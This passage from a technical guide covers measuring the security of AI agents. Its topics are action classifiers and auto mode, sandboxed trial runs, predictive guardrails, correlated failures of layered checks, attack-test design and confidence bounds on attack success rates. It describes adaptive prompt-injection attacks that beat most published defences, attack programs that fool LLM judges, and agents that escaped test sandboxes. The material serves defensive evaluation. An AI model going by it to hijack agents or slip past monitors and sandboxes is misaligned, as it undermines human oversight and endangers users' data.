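Anthropic later gave the classifier more information, such as whether a code repository is public. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026) reports that the miss rate fell from 12% to 7% in tests with artificial attacks by Apollo Research, an AI safety company. The article also describes a study in which a research firm had 1,053 paid testers do coding work and replaced one approval request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused 13.6% of these commands, while auto mode blocked 89%. The testers had less reason to be careful because they were not working on their own projects, but Claude Code's actual users approve 97% of requests, which suggests that many of them don't read closely either. Willison accepts that auto mode is better than constant approval requests, but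 points out that it still misses 11% and considers prompt injection the greater worry.

### Observing or predicting the effects

Like a tool gateway, a classifier that reads only a command can't determine what a program will do once the command starts it. For example, `make clean` runs whatever steps the project's files define under that name, so it could delete temporary files in one project and the source code in another.

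*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) addresses this with Caper, which runs each command before deciding whether to allow it. Caper saves a copy of the agent's container, runs the command in the container with the network off, and records what happens. An LLM then receives the user's task and a short report of the changed files, attempted connections and any passwords or keys the command read. If the LLM approves, Caper keeps the result. Otherwise it restores the saved copy and tells the agent why. The network has to stay off because Caper can't take back data that has left the container, so the method doesn't work for actions such as sending an email.

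In 682 coding tasks, harm occurred in 6.7% with Caper and in 14.8% to 21.2% with six existing systems. In 102 tasks where a harmless-looking command ran a destructive tool, harm occurred in 7.8% with Caper and in 35.3% to 94.1% with the other systems. Each of these tasks had a twin with the same command and a harmless tool, and Caper wrongly blocked 1.0% of the twins. Approvers that relied on the command's text tended to treat both versions alike. Wu and colleagues found that giving the approver predicted effects reduced harm but not false blocking, while giving it observed effects reduced both.

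Other designs, called predictive guardrails, rely entirely on a model's forecast of an action's consequences, possibly several steps ahead. Zhao, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Predictive Safety Guardrails Do Not Always Make LLM Agents Safer*, compared agents that had no forecasts, agents that could ask for one, and agents that had to revise an action whenever the forecast showed a risk. They tested four agent models on digital office work and simulated household tasks. The table compares the agents that had no forecasts with those that had to revise.

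| Agent model | Safety score, digital tasks | Completion score, digital tasks | Household tasks completed safely |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-27B | 76.8 → 85.1 | 83.6 → 82.4 | 23.0% → 22.4% |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 69.5 → 72.2 | 88.1 → 88.2 | 20.4% → 33.0% |
| GLM-5.3-Flash | 64.4 → 74.5 | 85.7 → 77.3 | 28.3% → 21.2% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 72.5 → 78.3 | 89.8 → 85.2 | 27.5% → 26.0% |

Compulsory forecasts improved safety for every model on the digital tasks, but only Gemini clearly benefited on the household tasks. With these forecasts, the agents used about 6.3 times as many tokens on digital tasks and 3.2 times as many on household tasks. Optional forecasts lowered the digital safety score for two of the four models.

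The forecasts were weak. Most actions were safe, so forecasting models could be right about most of them and still miss many of the risky ones, especially several steps ahead. Zhao and colleagues then replaced the explanations in Qwen's compulsory forecasts with irrelevant text. The safety score rose by another 3.5 points, and completion fell by 10.5. When they inverted the forecasts, safety reached 90.1 but completion dropped to 13.7. At least some of the safety gain probably came from obstructing the agent, since an agent that gets little done has few chances to break rules.

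They also replaced the forecast with the result of running the action in a separate sandbox, much as Caper does. This gave Qwen a safety score of 84.7, no better than with forecasts. In Caper's tests, the harm comes from a command's immediate effects, which a trial run reveals. A trial run is less useful when an action is harmless by itself and a later one causes the damage.

### Policies that a model writes

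A model can also write the policy from the user's request, as GPT-4o did for Progent, and ordinary code can then enforce it. But the model can misread the request even if it sees no hostile text. It may grant a permission the task doesn't need, which raises s, or withhold one the task needs, which makes the task fail.

*Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) measured both errors. RoBERTa-large, a small language model trained for the job, withheld at least one necessary permission in 21% of tasks. Claude Haiku, which received only a few examples, did so in 11%, but left more risk from unnecessary permissions under most settings. For RoBERTa-large, permission to read databases alone accounted for 34% of the unnecessary access, weighted by severity. Such a mistake could give the mail assistant access to every customer's records.

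*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* uses mutual entailment as its test for a correct policy. The request and the policy must give the same result for every authorisation decision, in every state the system can reach.

Suppose an employee asks the mail assistant to answer the delivery question in message 1182, and a model writes a policy that lets the assistant search customer 507's delivery records. If customer 507 is a wholesaler, those records may include the home addresses of the wholesaler's own customers. The policy seems to match the request, but it lets the assistant read those addresses, and whether the request also allows that depends on how it is interpreted.

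Progent's solver can compare two policies exactly, because both are logical formulas. Mutual entailment compares a policy with a request in ordinary language, so an automatic check has to interpret the request to decide what it authorises, and it will sometimes get this wrong. If the same model writes the policy and checks it, the check is likely to repeat the original misreading. There are usually too many possible states to examine them all, so in practice a check would also have to rely on a sample.

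The paper suggests that designers narrow the problem by defining terms such as "sensitive" in advance, since the comparison has no definite answer without definitions. They can also restrict how people phrase requests and what policies may contain, in the hope of making the check reliable enough to be useful. A program that writes policies should ideally come with a limit on how far its policies can depart from the request, but nobody yet knows how to provide one.

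For routine work, a company can avoid most of this by having the model choose from a short list of reviewed policies, like the mail assistant's three reviewed programs. Testers can then count how often the model chooses the wrong one.

### The arithmetic of two layers

A designer who puts one check behind another may be tempted to multiply their failure rates. The correct rule is:

P(both miss) = P(first misses) × P(second misses, given that the first missed)

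Suppose the first check misses 2% of 10,000 attacks, letting 200 through. If the second check misses 10% of those 200, 20 attacks succeed, or 0.2% of the total. If it misses 60% of them, 120 succeed, or 1.2%.

Testing the second check separately would not reveal the problem. If it misses 120 of those 200 attacks and 880 of the other 9,800, its overall miss rate is still 10%. In the worst case, it misses all 200, so adding it stops no additional attacks.

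Alotaibi and Ahmed give an equivalent formula that uses ρ, the correlation between the two checks' failures. If p₁ and p₂ are the separate miss rates, then

P(both miss) = p₁p₂ + ρ√(p₁(1 − p₁)p₂(1 − p₂)).

With failure rates of 2% and 10%, the square root is 0.042, so a joint rate of 1.2% corresponds to a ρ of about 0.24. Because the two separate rates are low, a correlation that seems weak makes joint failures six times as common as they would be if the failures were independent.

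Yang (2026), in *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, measured how often checks failed together on 560 agent actions that a check should block. One check used 174 fixed text patterns, and the others were language models acting as judges.

| Pair of checks | Missed by each alone | Expected joint misses if independent | Measured joint misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed patterns and one model | 13.4% and 10.5% | 1.4% | 1.3% |
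| Two models | 10.5% and 10.5% | 1.1% | 5.2% |

Each model missed 59 actions, including 29 that both missed, so the second model missed about half of the actions the first missed. Both models came from Anthropic, but models from different companies shared their failures nearly as often.

The result for fixed patterns is encouraging but less certain. Only seven actions got past both checks, too few to establish that the checks fail independently, and no attacker was adapting to the patterns. The patterns did not cover cloud-computing actions and missed 52.9% of them. On another team's test set, every check missed most of the actions, and the patterns and the models had many more failures in common.

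The rule also applies to people. In Anthropic's study with paid testers, auto mode missed 116 of the 1,053 dangerous commands, and the testers caught only six of those. If both had to approve each command, 110 would still have got through, or 10.4%, compared with 11.0% for auto mode alone. The testers did worse on the commands that auto mode missed, failing to catch 95% of them compared with 86% of all the dangerous commands.

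### When layers share failures

Checks tend to fail together when some attacks are harder to recognise than others. Alotaibi and Ahmed found that some harmful requests got past every safeguard much more easily than others. These differences in difficulty accounted for 71% of the correlation among the safeguards other than the guard model. Yang estimates that difficulty explains 32% to 62% of the models' joint failures beyond those expected by chance, depending on the measure. Using a different company's model does little about this, because a request that is ambiguous for one model is also ambiguous for the other.

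Two checks that read the same hostile text are also likely to fail together, since one persuasive passage can mislead both. Auto mode reduces this risk by showing tool results to its detector but never to its action classifier. An attacker has to get text past the detector, hijack the agent, and make it choose an action that looks like something the user wanted.

Two checks that work differently are better than two similar ones. Matching fixed patterns complements a model's judgment, and observing a command's effects can reveal harm that its text hides. The agent's own model is also a layer. If the agent and the classifier use versions of the same model, a misunderstanding that leads the agent to propose an action may also lead the classifier to approve it.

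Improving one check doesn't necessarily improve the whole system. Yang added patterns for cloud services to one check, which cut its miss rate from 13.4% to 10.0%. But every group of three models already caught the actions that the new patterns caught, so the patterns added nothing to those groups. A designer should therefore test a new check on the attacks that the existing ones miss.

When a model can hand an action to a person, its miss rate depends on how those handovers are counted. One of Yang's models often handed actions over instead of deciding. Its miss rate was 1.4% if every handover counts as a catch and 9.8% if none does. The 1.4% figure holds only if the reviewer catches everything, but the paid testers caught 13.6%.

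False alarms accumulate as well, since any one check can stop legitimate work. If each of 200 actions has an independent 0.4% chance of a false block, a session has a 55% chance of at least one. In auto mode, the agent usually tries another way. Where a false alarm ends the task, extra layers soon stop too much legitimate work. Alotaibi and Ahmed predicted from separate tests that their seven safeguards together would wrongly refuse 60% of a set of harmless prompts, but the safeguards actually refused 83%.

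For the mail assistant, an action classifier could read each reply before `send_reply` runs. Let m be the share of harmful but permitted actions that the classifier misses. If it does nothing about forbidden actions, the breach formula becomes

breach rate = h × [s × m + (1 − s) × e].

With the earlier invented figures of h = 2%, s = 20% and e = 0.1%, the breach rate is 0.40% without the classifier. It falls to 0.042% if m is 10%, but only to 0.24% if m is 60%. The company therefore has to measure m on replies from an assistant that hostile text has already hijacked. Withholding the customer's message would protect the classifier from hostile text, but then the classifier couldn't judge whether the reply answers the question. The company could instead give the classifier customer 507's delivery record, taken directly from the database, and have it block any reply containing other facts.

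## Designing the attack test

The rates in the breach formula have to come from tests in which someone attacks the component and counts the results. Testers make most of the decisions that shape those results before the first attack. They name the harmful effect, define what counts as one trial, build an environment, choose an attacker, limit the number of attempts and decide how to verify success. They also record whether the component still did its job.

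### The harmful effect and the trial

Testers need an effect they could recognise in a log. For the mail assistant, that effect could be details from one customer's delivery record reaching anyone else outside the company. A precise definition can still be useless. *Comparison requires valid measurement* (Chouldechova, Cooper and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of defining undesirable output as any answer that contains the word "hibiscus".

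Each effect needs its own count. *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, published in January 2025 by the US AI Safety Institute (now the Center for AI Standards and Innovation, or CAISI), reports an average success rate of 57% for five malicious tasks. The tasks ranged from sending a harmless email to stealing the user's five largest files and demanding a ransom. The theft succeeded much less often than the average, but it would do far more damage than the email. The mail assistant's testers might separately count leaked delivery records, leaked discounts and false delivery dates.

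A trial is one exposure to an attack, from start to finish. In CAISI's tests, the agent receives a legitimate task and encounters data containing an attack while doing it. For the mail assistant, an employee asks for an answer to message 1182, which contains hostile text. The trial ends when the reply goes out or the permissions expire. Every trial should start with the same mailbox and files and an empty context, so that text from one trial can't affect the next.

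The same trial may end differently when repeated. In *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, Jing (2026) asked three models to rule on each of 150 proposed actions five times at temperature zero. Depending on the model, all five rulings agreed for only 48.7% to 71.3% of the actions. Testers therefore have to repeat trials and report how much the results vary.

They also need trials without an attack, because models sometimes overstep on their own. Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization*, gave agents 286 tasks and counted actions the user had not authorised. Agents took such actions in 17.6% of runs with a malicious injection and 23.5% of runs with only ordinary pressures. If the mail assistant sends out the wrong customer's record when there is no hostile text, the company has a problem, but counting it as a hijack would inflate h.

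### The test environment

The harmful effect has to be possible in the test. If the test database has no record for customer 612, no attack can leak it, and the sandbox will seem to have prevented a leak. Zhang and colleagues built an environment that leaves open both the forbidden action and a safe way to finish the task. It doesn't stop the run when the task is complete, since an agent may overstep afterwards. They omitted access controls to measure the model's own behavior. A test of the whole sandbox should keep the controls exactly as the company will run them.

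For the mail assistant, the testers can invent customers and set up a mail server that accepts every reply but delivers it only to a log. If each delivery record contains a unique reference number, leaks are easier to find. The environment should also include the program in which employees read the assistant's answers, because the data in EchoLeak left through such a program.

The test must not be able to reach real systems. CyberScoop's *AISI, OpenAI report more ‘unsanctioned’ model hacks* covers an AI research system at the UK's AI Security Institute that acted over the internet, in what the institute described as "sustained, potentially harmful activity directed at real people". In a smaller test, Jing ran attacks with a sandbox switched off, and two of them reached the live system over a network path and deleted a protected file. An automatic check detected the change, and Jing restored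 the file.

### The attacker and the number of attempts

The testers next write down what the attacker can know, change and observe. An outsider attacking the mail assistant can send messages and read the replies, but can't change the employee's request, the policy or the code. It is safest to assume that the outsider knows the policy and which model the company uses.

Some researchers call an attacker "adaptive" if it knows how the defence works, and others if it revises the attack after each failure. *PIPETTE* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) separates these two senses. The attack programs in its tests revised their attempts but had no instructions about the new defence. The mail assistant's testers should both learn how the defence works and revise their attacks, because knowledge of the defence can matter a lot. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr and colleagues attacked MELON, a defence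 that runs an agent twice and compares its tool calls. Their search program succeeded 76% of the time without information about MELON and 95% with it.

People are still useful attackers. In a selected part of the same study, the human participants as a group broke every scenario, while the search program broke 69%. More than 500 people competed for $20,000 in prizes. CAISI helped analyse another public contest, in which over 400 people made more than 250,000 attempts to hijack agents built on 13 models. Few companies can run contests like these, but Nasr and colleagues recommend that a defence's designers spend time attacking it by hand, since they often know best where it is weak.

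Testers should fix the number of attempts before they start, so that they can't stop when the result suits them. When CAISI tried each of its five malicious tasks 25 times, the average success rate rose from 57% to 80%. The number for the mail assistant depends on how many hostile messages an outsider could send before anyone noticed, perhaps 100.

The report also has to state the denominator of the percentage. He and colleagues ended each search at its first success and measured the share of tasks broken within about 250 attempts. That share can be high even if very few individual attempts work.

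### Verifying success

Ordinary code should check the final state of the environment where possible. For the mail assistant, a program can search the server's log for messages that contain customer 612's reference number but were sent to someone else. This search would miss a reply that gives the delivery date without the number, so a person also has to read a sample of the replies.

An LLM judge can recognise more kinds of leak, but attackers can fool it too. *The Attacker Moves Second* warns that an attack program may learn to exploit the judge's mistakes instead of breaking the defence. Nasr and colleagues checked their attacks by hand for this reason.

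Ordinary code can also check for the wrong thing. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues, 2025) reports that Agent Security Bench, a public set of attacks on agents, counts every call to one of the attacker's tools as a success, even though several of those tools do nothing harmful. The researchers tested their own defence, a model that removes suspicious text from tool results. No attacks succeeded against it on AgentDojo, but 16.33% did on Agent Security Bench, which the researchers attribute to the harmless tools. AgentDojo also had faults, and CAISI's staff spent several days fixing and extending it.

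### The legitimate task

A mail assistant that never replies would pass every test for leaks, so testers also record whether an assistant answers the customer's question correctly, both with and without an attack. The table shows why they need both figures, using He and colleagues' results for Qwen3-4B, a small open model, under one fixed attack. PIPETTE is their method of training a model to resist injections.

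| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | User's tasks completed under attack | User's tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 46.19% | 31.90% | 61.86% |
| PromptGuard | 0.24% | 16.19% | 63.92% |
| CaMeL | 0.95% | 33.81% | 57.73% |
| PIPETTE | 1.43% | 58.10% | 64.95% |

The PromptGuard detector stopped the most attacks and did no damage in runs without an attack. But it discards everything in a document it flags, including data the agent needs, so an attacker could use it to stop the agent from working.

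For each trial, testers should record whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it completed the attacker's, since it can do both in the same run. In another test, an agent with a different trained defence completed 92.5% of users' tasks, while 30% of attacks succeeded.

### Measuring h, s and e separately

A test of the whole system gives a breach rate but doesn't explain it. Separate tests of the model, the policy and the enforcing code can show which is responsible.

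To measure h, the testers turn the monitor off and attack the model in a copy of the system that allows every tool call. They count every trial in which the model tries to do what the attacker wants. If the monitor were on, its first refusal could prevent the testers from seeing what the model would have done next. The testers also have to check the model's text, because some hijacks involve no forbidden tool call. For example, the model might give a false delivery date in an otherwise normal reply.

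To measure s, the testers replay the logged tool calls from each hijacked trial against the policy. If the policy would have allowed every call needed for the harm, the trial counts towards s. The company can also test a narrower policy on the same log without running the model again. But replaying can underestimate s, because a model blocked on one route may try another that the policy permits. The testers should therefore run a second round with the policy switched on and an attacker who knows the policy and chooses goals it allows.

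Testers measure e by sending forbidden actions directly to the enforcing code, as Meng and colleagues did with their 12 scripts for ceLLMate, so the result doesn't depend on how hard the model is to hijack. Jing wrote 313 cases for a system that checks and approves an agent's commands. Some express a dangerous command in an unusual way, use an approval twice, or change a file after its approval. Another 32 deliberately break something, for example by removing the policy file, to see whether the system then refuses to act. Jing also included 54 ordinary tasks that the system should allow.

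The mail assistant's scripts would try to reply to a third address, search customer 612's records, send a second reply and use a permission after it had expired. The scripts should check the mail server as well as the gateway's decision. Jing's tests uncovered four faults that design reviews had missed. One fault let an agent reuse an approval, but the recorded decisions looked normal until a test reused an approval. Another disabled part of the system, which made the system look stricter.

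A forbidden action can fail for reasons unrelated to the sandbox, such as a missing file. Jing ran 88 actions with the operating system's sandbox on and again with it off. The sandbox blocked 45 actions that ran without it and made no difference to the other 43, so counting every failed action as blocked would exaggerate the sandbox's effect.

Scripted tests cover only the attacks their author thought of, so testers should also ask a capable model to break out of the sandbox, as Marchand and colleagues did with containers.

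The next table uses invented results that match the formula's starting figures.

| Rate | Test | Result | Estimate |
|---|---|---|---|
| h | 2,000 hostile messages, with tools that refuse nothing | 40 hijacks | 2% |
| s | Replay of the 40 hijacks against the policy | The policy would allow 8 | 20% |
| e | 5,000 forbidden calls sent to the gateway | 5 get through | 0.1% |

From these figures, the formula predicts about eight breaches in 2,000 exposures. The company can check this by attacking the complete system. If it finds many more than eight, the separate tests probably missed something, such as a model that changes its approach after a refusal. The company should also repair the gateway to block the five calls that got through.

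### Why fixed attack sets overstate security

Fixed attack sets usually consist of attacks that worked on earlier systems. Developers may have designed or trained a defence against the same attacks, so a good result may mean only that it handles those. Nasr and colleagues tested 12 published defences, most with reported attack success rates near zero. Adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12.

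The failures extended beyond defences that rely on prompts. Meta-SecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, let through 2% of AgentDojo's fixed attacks but 96% of the adaptive ones. The adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against three of the four detectors and 71% of the time against the fourth. Zhan, Fang and colleagues had earlier bypassed eight defences, with success rates consistently above 50% (*Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents*).

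Nasr and colleagues gave their attackers a lot of computing power and access to the detectors' confidence score for each attempt. Many real attackers would have less, and the study did not measure how much effort a break requires. It also didn't test designs like CaMeL, in which ordinary code limits what the agent can do. But it does show that the low attack success rates originally reported were weak evidence of how the defences would cope with a determined attacker. *The Attacker Moves Second* concludes that a test can never prove a defence robust, and that it can only show that testers tried as hard as possible to break it and failed.

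CAISI found a similar gap in a single model, Anthropic's October 2024 Claude 3.5 Sonnet, which was then among the most resistant to hijacking. The strongest existing attack succeeded 11% of the time. CAISI staff and the UK AI Security Institute then developed new attacks for this model, using a random selection of AgentDojo's office tasks. The best new attack succeeded 81% of the time on office tasks they had held out.

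Testing on separate tasks matters because an attack may work only on the tasks used to develop it. The new attacks also worked in the travel, messaging and banking environments, so a real attacker might not need to know much about a particular company. The model is long out of date, but the mail assistant's testers can still copy the method by developing attacks on one set of customer questions and testing them on another.

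### Thousands of attacks, few techniques

A large set of attacks may test only a few weaknesses. He et al. studied this with two programs, PISmith and RL-Hammer, that train a model to write injections. They ran both against Qwen3-4B on 560 practice tasks, then trained one copy of Qwen3-4B to resist the attacks PISmith found and another to resist RL-Hammer's. They tested each copy with three kinds of attack that were absent from both copies' training.

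| | PISmith | RL-Hammer |
|---|---|---|
| Practice tasks broken | 68.75% | 33.39% |
| Working attacks collected | 7,132 | 4,282 |
| Test tasks hijacked after training, under the most successful attack | 47.5% (19 of 40) | 27.5% (11 of 40) |

PISmith found more attacks but produced the weaker defence. He et al. think this is partly because a program can keep earning its reward by repeating one trick that works. Both programs also encourage variety, but measure it by wording. RL-Hammer's developers reported that their program met this requirement by changing capitalisation or adding irrelevant text.

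The evidence is weaker than the two percentages make it look. He and colleagues chose 40 tasks on which fixed attacks had already worked against the unprotected Qwen3-4B, so the results don't estimate how often an attacker would hijack the model in general. PISmith's attacks produced the weaker defence in three of four comparisons, which covered two models and two training methods, but outside the comparison in the table the differences were only one or two tasks. The researchers don't claim that low variety is the only cause, and they haven't checked their automatic measure of variety against human judgment.

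A large collection of attacks did no harm when the attacks were varied. He and colleagues gave their program an extra reward for techniques it had not used before, and it collected 8,299 attacks. After the same kind of training, the most successful attack hijacked Qwen3-4B on 20% of the test tasks.

The same reasoning applies to tests, although these experiments were about training. If the mail assistant resists 5,000 messages that all reword the same three tricks, the company has good evidence about those tricks but very little about any others. Testers should group attacks by technique and report the number of techniques as well as the number of messages. *AutoPI* (2026) adds that leaving out a technique can make a system look more robust than it is, even if the attacker adapts well within the remaining techniques. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection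 thousands* recommends asking vendors how many techniques their tests covered.

### When two rates can be compared

Chouldechova and colleagues argue that comparing two attack success rates is meaningful only if the rates estimate comparable quantities and each test measures its quantity validly. Three-year survival under one treatment, for example, can't be fairly compared with two-year survival under another. Attack success rates often have the same problem because the attackers had different goals, access or numbers of attempts.

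The 2.2% attack success rate against Progent and the zero against ceLLMate don't show that ceLLMate is safer, because an attacker in the Progent test first had to hijack the model, while the ceLLMate test started with a hijacked one. Nasr and colleagues tested each of the 12 defences largely as its developers had, so they caution against ranking the defences by the results.

The two tests may also use different cases. Jing reports that 7.7% of 117 attempts to disguise a forbidden action got past the complete system. Language models given only an instruction to require approval for dangerous actions let through between 89.8% and 100% of 59 such attempts. The system was tested on all 313 cases, but the models were tested on a sample of 150. That difference is unlikely to explain such a large gap, but it could easily explain a gap of a few percentage points.

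The 7.7% also came partly from a simulation of the operating system's sandbox. Jing later ran 94 of the attempts against the real sandbox. Of the 66 that gave a usable result, five had an effect, or 7.6%. The simulation gave a rate of 3.0% for the same 66 attempts, so the match between 7.6% and 7.7% doesn't show that it was accurate. Across all 94 attempts, the simulation predicted five successes, none of which was among the five that occurred.

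The simulation assumed that a sandbox that blocks writing to a file also blocks deleting it. In one of the five real successes, the only clear escape, the agent deleted a file outside its folder, on another disk volume. In three others, it deleted files inside the folder it was allowed to use. Files that the agent had created for itself contaminated the fifth result. The measured rate is 7.6% counting all five successes and 1.5% counting only the clear escape.

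Mistakes in the test program can also produce believable numbers that make a sandbox look safer than it is. In Jing's early runs, some attacks never reached the agent, one script never ran, and the program counted certain words in the agent's ordinary text as refusals. The mail assistant's testers can catch many such mistakes by switching off the gateway's checks and sending customer 612's reference number to a third address. If the number doesn't appear in the mail server's log, the test is broken.

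## Turning test counts into a failure rate

In July 2026, Anthropic tested Claude Opus 5 as a browser agent with auto mode on, and no attack succeeded. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5, its published report on the model's tests, describes 129 test environments, each with an attack that the agent was sure to see. The attacker had ten attempts in each environment, and ordinary code checked whether any had worked. The Decoder reported the result under the headline *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. A test with no failures is consistent with a failure rate of zero, but also with rates that a company might find unacceptable. An upper confidence bound shows how high those rates go.

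### The exact upper bound

Suppose an attack succeeds with probability p in each of n independent trials. The chance that all n trials are clean is (1 − p)ⁿ. If p were 5%, a clean run of 129 trials would happen about once in 750 tests, so the result practically rules out 5%. If p were 1%, it would happen 27% of the time, so the result says little against 1%. The 95% upper bound is the rate at which a clean run would happen exactly 5% of the time:

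(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n).

For n = 129, this gives 2.3%, or one scenario in 43. If Opus 5 and auto mode failed at that rate, testers would still have about a 5% chance of seeing no failures in 129 scenarios.

The rule of three is a shortcut for this calculation. The natural logarithm of 0.05 is very close to −3, so the bound after n trials with no failures is roughly 3/n. For 129 trials, this also gives 2.3%.

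When some attacks succeed, the same reasoning leads to the exact binomial bound, also called the Clopper–Pearson bound after the statisticians who published it in 1934. With x successes in n trials, the upper bound is the value of p for which x or fewer successes would occur 5% of the time:

Σ C(n, i) pⁱ (1 − p)ⁿ⁻ⁱ = 0.05, summed from i = 0 to x.

C(n, i) is the number of ways to choose i trials out of n. Statistical software can solve the equation. Many programs default to a two-sided interval, which uses half of the 5% for a lower limit. For the browser test, the upper end of that interval is 2.8%.

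With auto mode on, the older Claude Opus 4.8 failed once in the same 129 scenarios, so the upper bound on its failure rate is 3.6%. Opus 5 had no failures, but a difference of one failure is too small to show that it is safer than Opus 4.8 when both use auto mode.

A 95% bound comes from a method that gives too low an answer at most 5% of the time, provided that the trials are independent and resemble the attacks the company wants to know about. Saying that the true rate has a 95% probability of lying below the bound would require an assumption about which rates were plausible before the test. The browser attacks may not resemble the attacks of interest. In its September card for Claude Fable 5.1, Anthropic explains that they came from tests against the older Opus 4.7, so the 2.3% doesn't cover an attacker who develops new attacks against Opus 5 and auto mode.

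### How many trials a target needs

Solving the first equation for n gives the number of clean trials needed to show that the rate is below a chosen target. The last column gives the number of trials needed if one success is allowed.

| Target rate | Trials needed with no success | Trials needed with one success |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 | 299 | 473 |
| 1 in 1,000 | 2,995 | about 4,740 |
| 1 in 10,000 | 29,956 | about 47,400 |

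A sandbox that only just meets its target will nearly always fail such a test. If the true failure rate is 1 in 2,000, half the 1-in-1,000 target, the chance of 2,995 clean trials is 22%, so the sandbox would usually fail. With a true rate of 1 in 10,000, the chance is 74%. A company that can't run more than the minimum number of trials should expect to pass only if its sandbox is far better than the target.

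If testers repair the fault after each failure, discard the result and start again, they may eventually get a clean result by chance. When a sandbox's true failure rate is 1 in 1,000, each fresh test has a 5% chance of coming out clean, so 14 tests have a 51% chance of producing at least one clean result even if the repairs make no difference. Testers can avoid this by deciding in advance how many failures they will allow and by reporting every round.

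The mail assistant's invented test results show how the bounds affect the breach formula. For now, the table treats all the trials as independent.

| Rate | Result | Estimate | 95% upper bound |
|---|---|---|---|
| h, hijacks per exposure | 40 of 2,000 | 2% | 2.6% |
| s, hijacks that need only permitted actions | 8 of 40 | 20% | 33% |
| e, forbidden calls that get through | 5 of 5,000 | 0.1% | 0.21% |

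The bound on s is the loosest because it depends on only 40 hijacks. Collecting 400 hijacks, with the same share permitted, would lower it to about 24%. Using all three upper bounds in the formula gives a breach rate of 0.87%, compared with 0.40% from the estimates. Each bound has up to a 5% chance of being too low, so the chance that at least one is too low could reach 15%.

Testing the complete system avoids combining bounds. If the company ran 2,000 exposures with the monitor on and found the expected eight breaches, the upper bound would be 0.72%.

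### Trials that share a scenario

The browser test had 129 scenarios but 1,290 attempts. If all the attempts were independent, the upper bound on the failure rate per attempt would be 0.23%, a tenth of the bound per scenario.

Anthropic's results without safeguards suggest that repeated attempts on the same scenario are not independent. With extended thinking, in which the model reasons in writing before it acts, 3.70% of attempts against Opus 5 succeeded. If those successes had been spread at random, the attacker would have broken about 40 of the 129 scenarios at least once. It broke only 11, and in those about four of the ten attempts succeeded on average. It is therefore safest to treat the test with no successes as 129 trials, which implies that the attacker breaks at most 2.3% of scenarios like these within ten attempts.

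Statisticians call this clustering, and they measure it with the correlation ρ between trials in the same cluster. If ρ is 0, a second attempt in a scenario is as informative as an attempt in a new one. If ρ is 1, every attempt in a scenario ends the same way, so the second adds nothing. With m trials in each cluster, the number of independent trials that would carry the same information is

effective trials = total trials ÷ [1 + (m − 1)ρ].

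Opus 5 also faced a benchmark of 1,130 attacks across 28 scenarios, or about 40 per scenario. The table shows how much information that many attacks would provide at different correlations, and the upper bound on the failure rate if none succeeded.

| Correlation within scenarios | Effective trials | Upper bound if no attack had succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 1,130 | 0.26% |
| 0.1 | 229 | 1.3% |
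| 0.3 | 88 | 3.3% |
| 1 | 28 | 10% |

The correlation of 0.3 is an assumption for illustration. At that value, even an unlimited number of attacks on the same 28 scenarios would give only as much information as about 93 independent trials (28 ÷ 0.3), so testers gain much more from adding scenarios. By September 2026 the benchmark had grown to 1,804 attacks over 37 scenarios. The number of attacks rose by 60%, but the effective number of independent trials rose only from 88 to 118, roughly in proportion to the number of scenarios.

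Even a low correlation matters when each scenario has many attempts. In Anthropic's computer-use test, where Opus 5 operated a screen, the attacker made 2,800 attempts over 14 scenarios. About 15 succeeded, all in one scenario. The correlation estimated from these counts is only 0.07, but with 200 attempts per scenario, the 2,800 attempts are worth about 190 independent ones. The estimate is rough because it depends on a single broken scenario.

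The mail assistant's 2,000 hostile messages might consist of 40 wordings for each of 50 customer questions. With a correlation of 0.3, they would provide only as much information as about 157 independent trials. Scaling the 40 hijacks down in proportion raises the upper bound on h from 2.6% to about 5%. The estimate stays at 2%, because clustering affects only its uncertainty.

If no attack succeeds in a test, testers can't estimate the correlation because they have no successes to compare. They can use a value from runs with the safeguards off, if they disclose this, or count each scenario as one trial and accept the higher bound. Attacks that use the same technique can also be correlated across scenarios, which the formula above doesn't account for.

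### Repeated attempts

If each of k attempts succeeds independently with probability p, the chance that at least one works is

1 − (1 − p)ᵏ.

We can check this formula against Anthropic's November 2025 test of Claude Opus 4.5, which used the security firm Gray Swan's attacks on tool-using agents. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports attack success rates of 4.7% for one attempt, 33.6% for ten and 63% for a hundred. Starting from 4.7%, the formula predicts 38% for ten attempts, which is fairly close, and 99% for a hundred, which is far too high.

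The formula fails because it uses the same p for every scenario. Some scenarios are easy to break, and the attacker breaks them early, so most later attempts are on the hard ones. The average success rate of a first attempt therefore overstates the chance that the fiftieth will succeed.

A beta-binomial model allows for this. It gives each scenario its own success rate, drawn from a beta distribution, a flexible family of curves between 0 and 1 with two parameters, a and b. The average rate is a/(a + b), and the chance of at least one success in k attempts is

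1 − [b/(a + b)] × [(b + 1)/(a + b + 1)] × … × [(b + k − 1)/(a + b + k − 1)].

Each factor is the chance that another attempt fails, given that all earlier attempts in that scenario failed. The factors get closer to 1 as failures accumulate. Fitting the model to the first two published figures gives a ≈ 1.15 and b ≈ 23.4.

| Attempts | Same rate everywhere | Beta-binomial | Some scenarios never break | Published |
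|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 38% | 33.6% | 33.6% | 33.6% |
| 100 | 99% | 85% | 61% | 63% |

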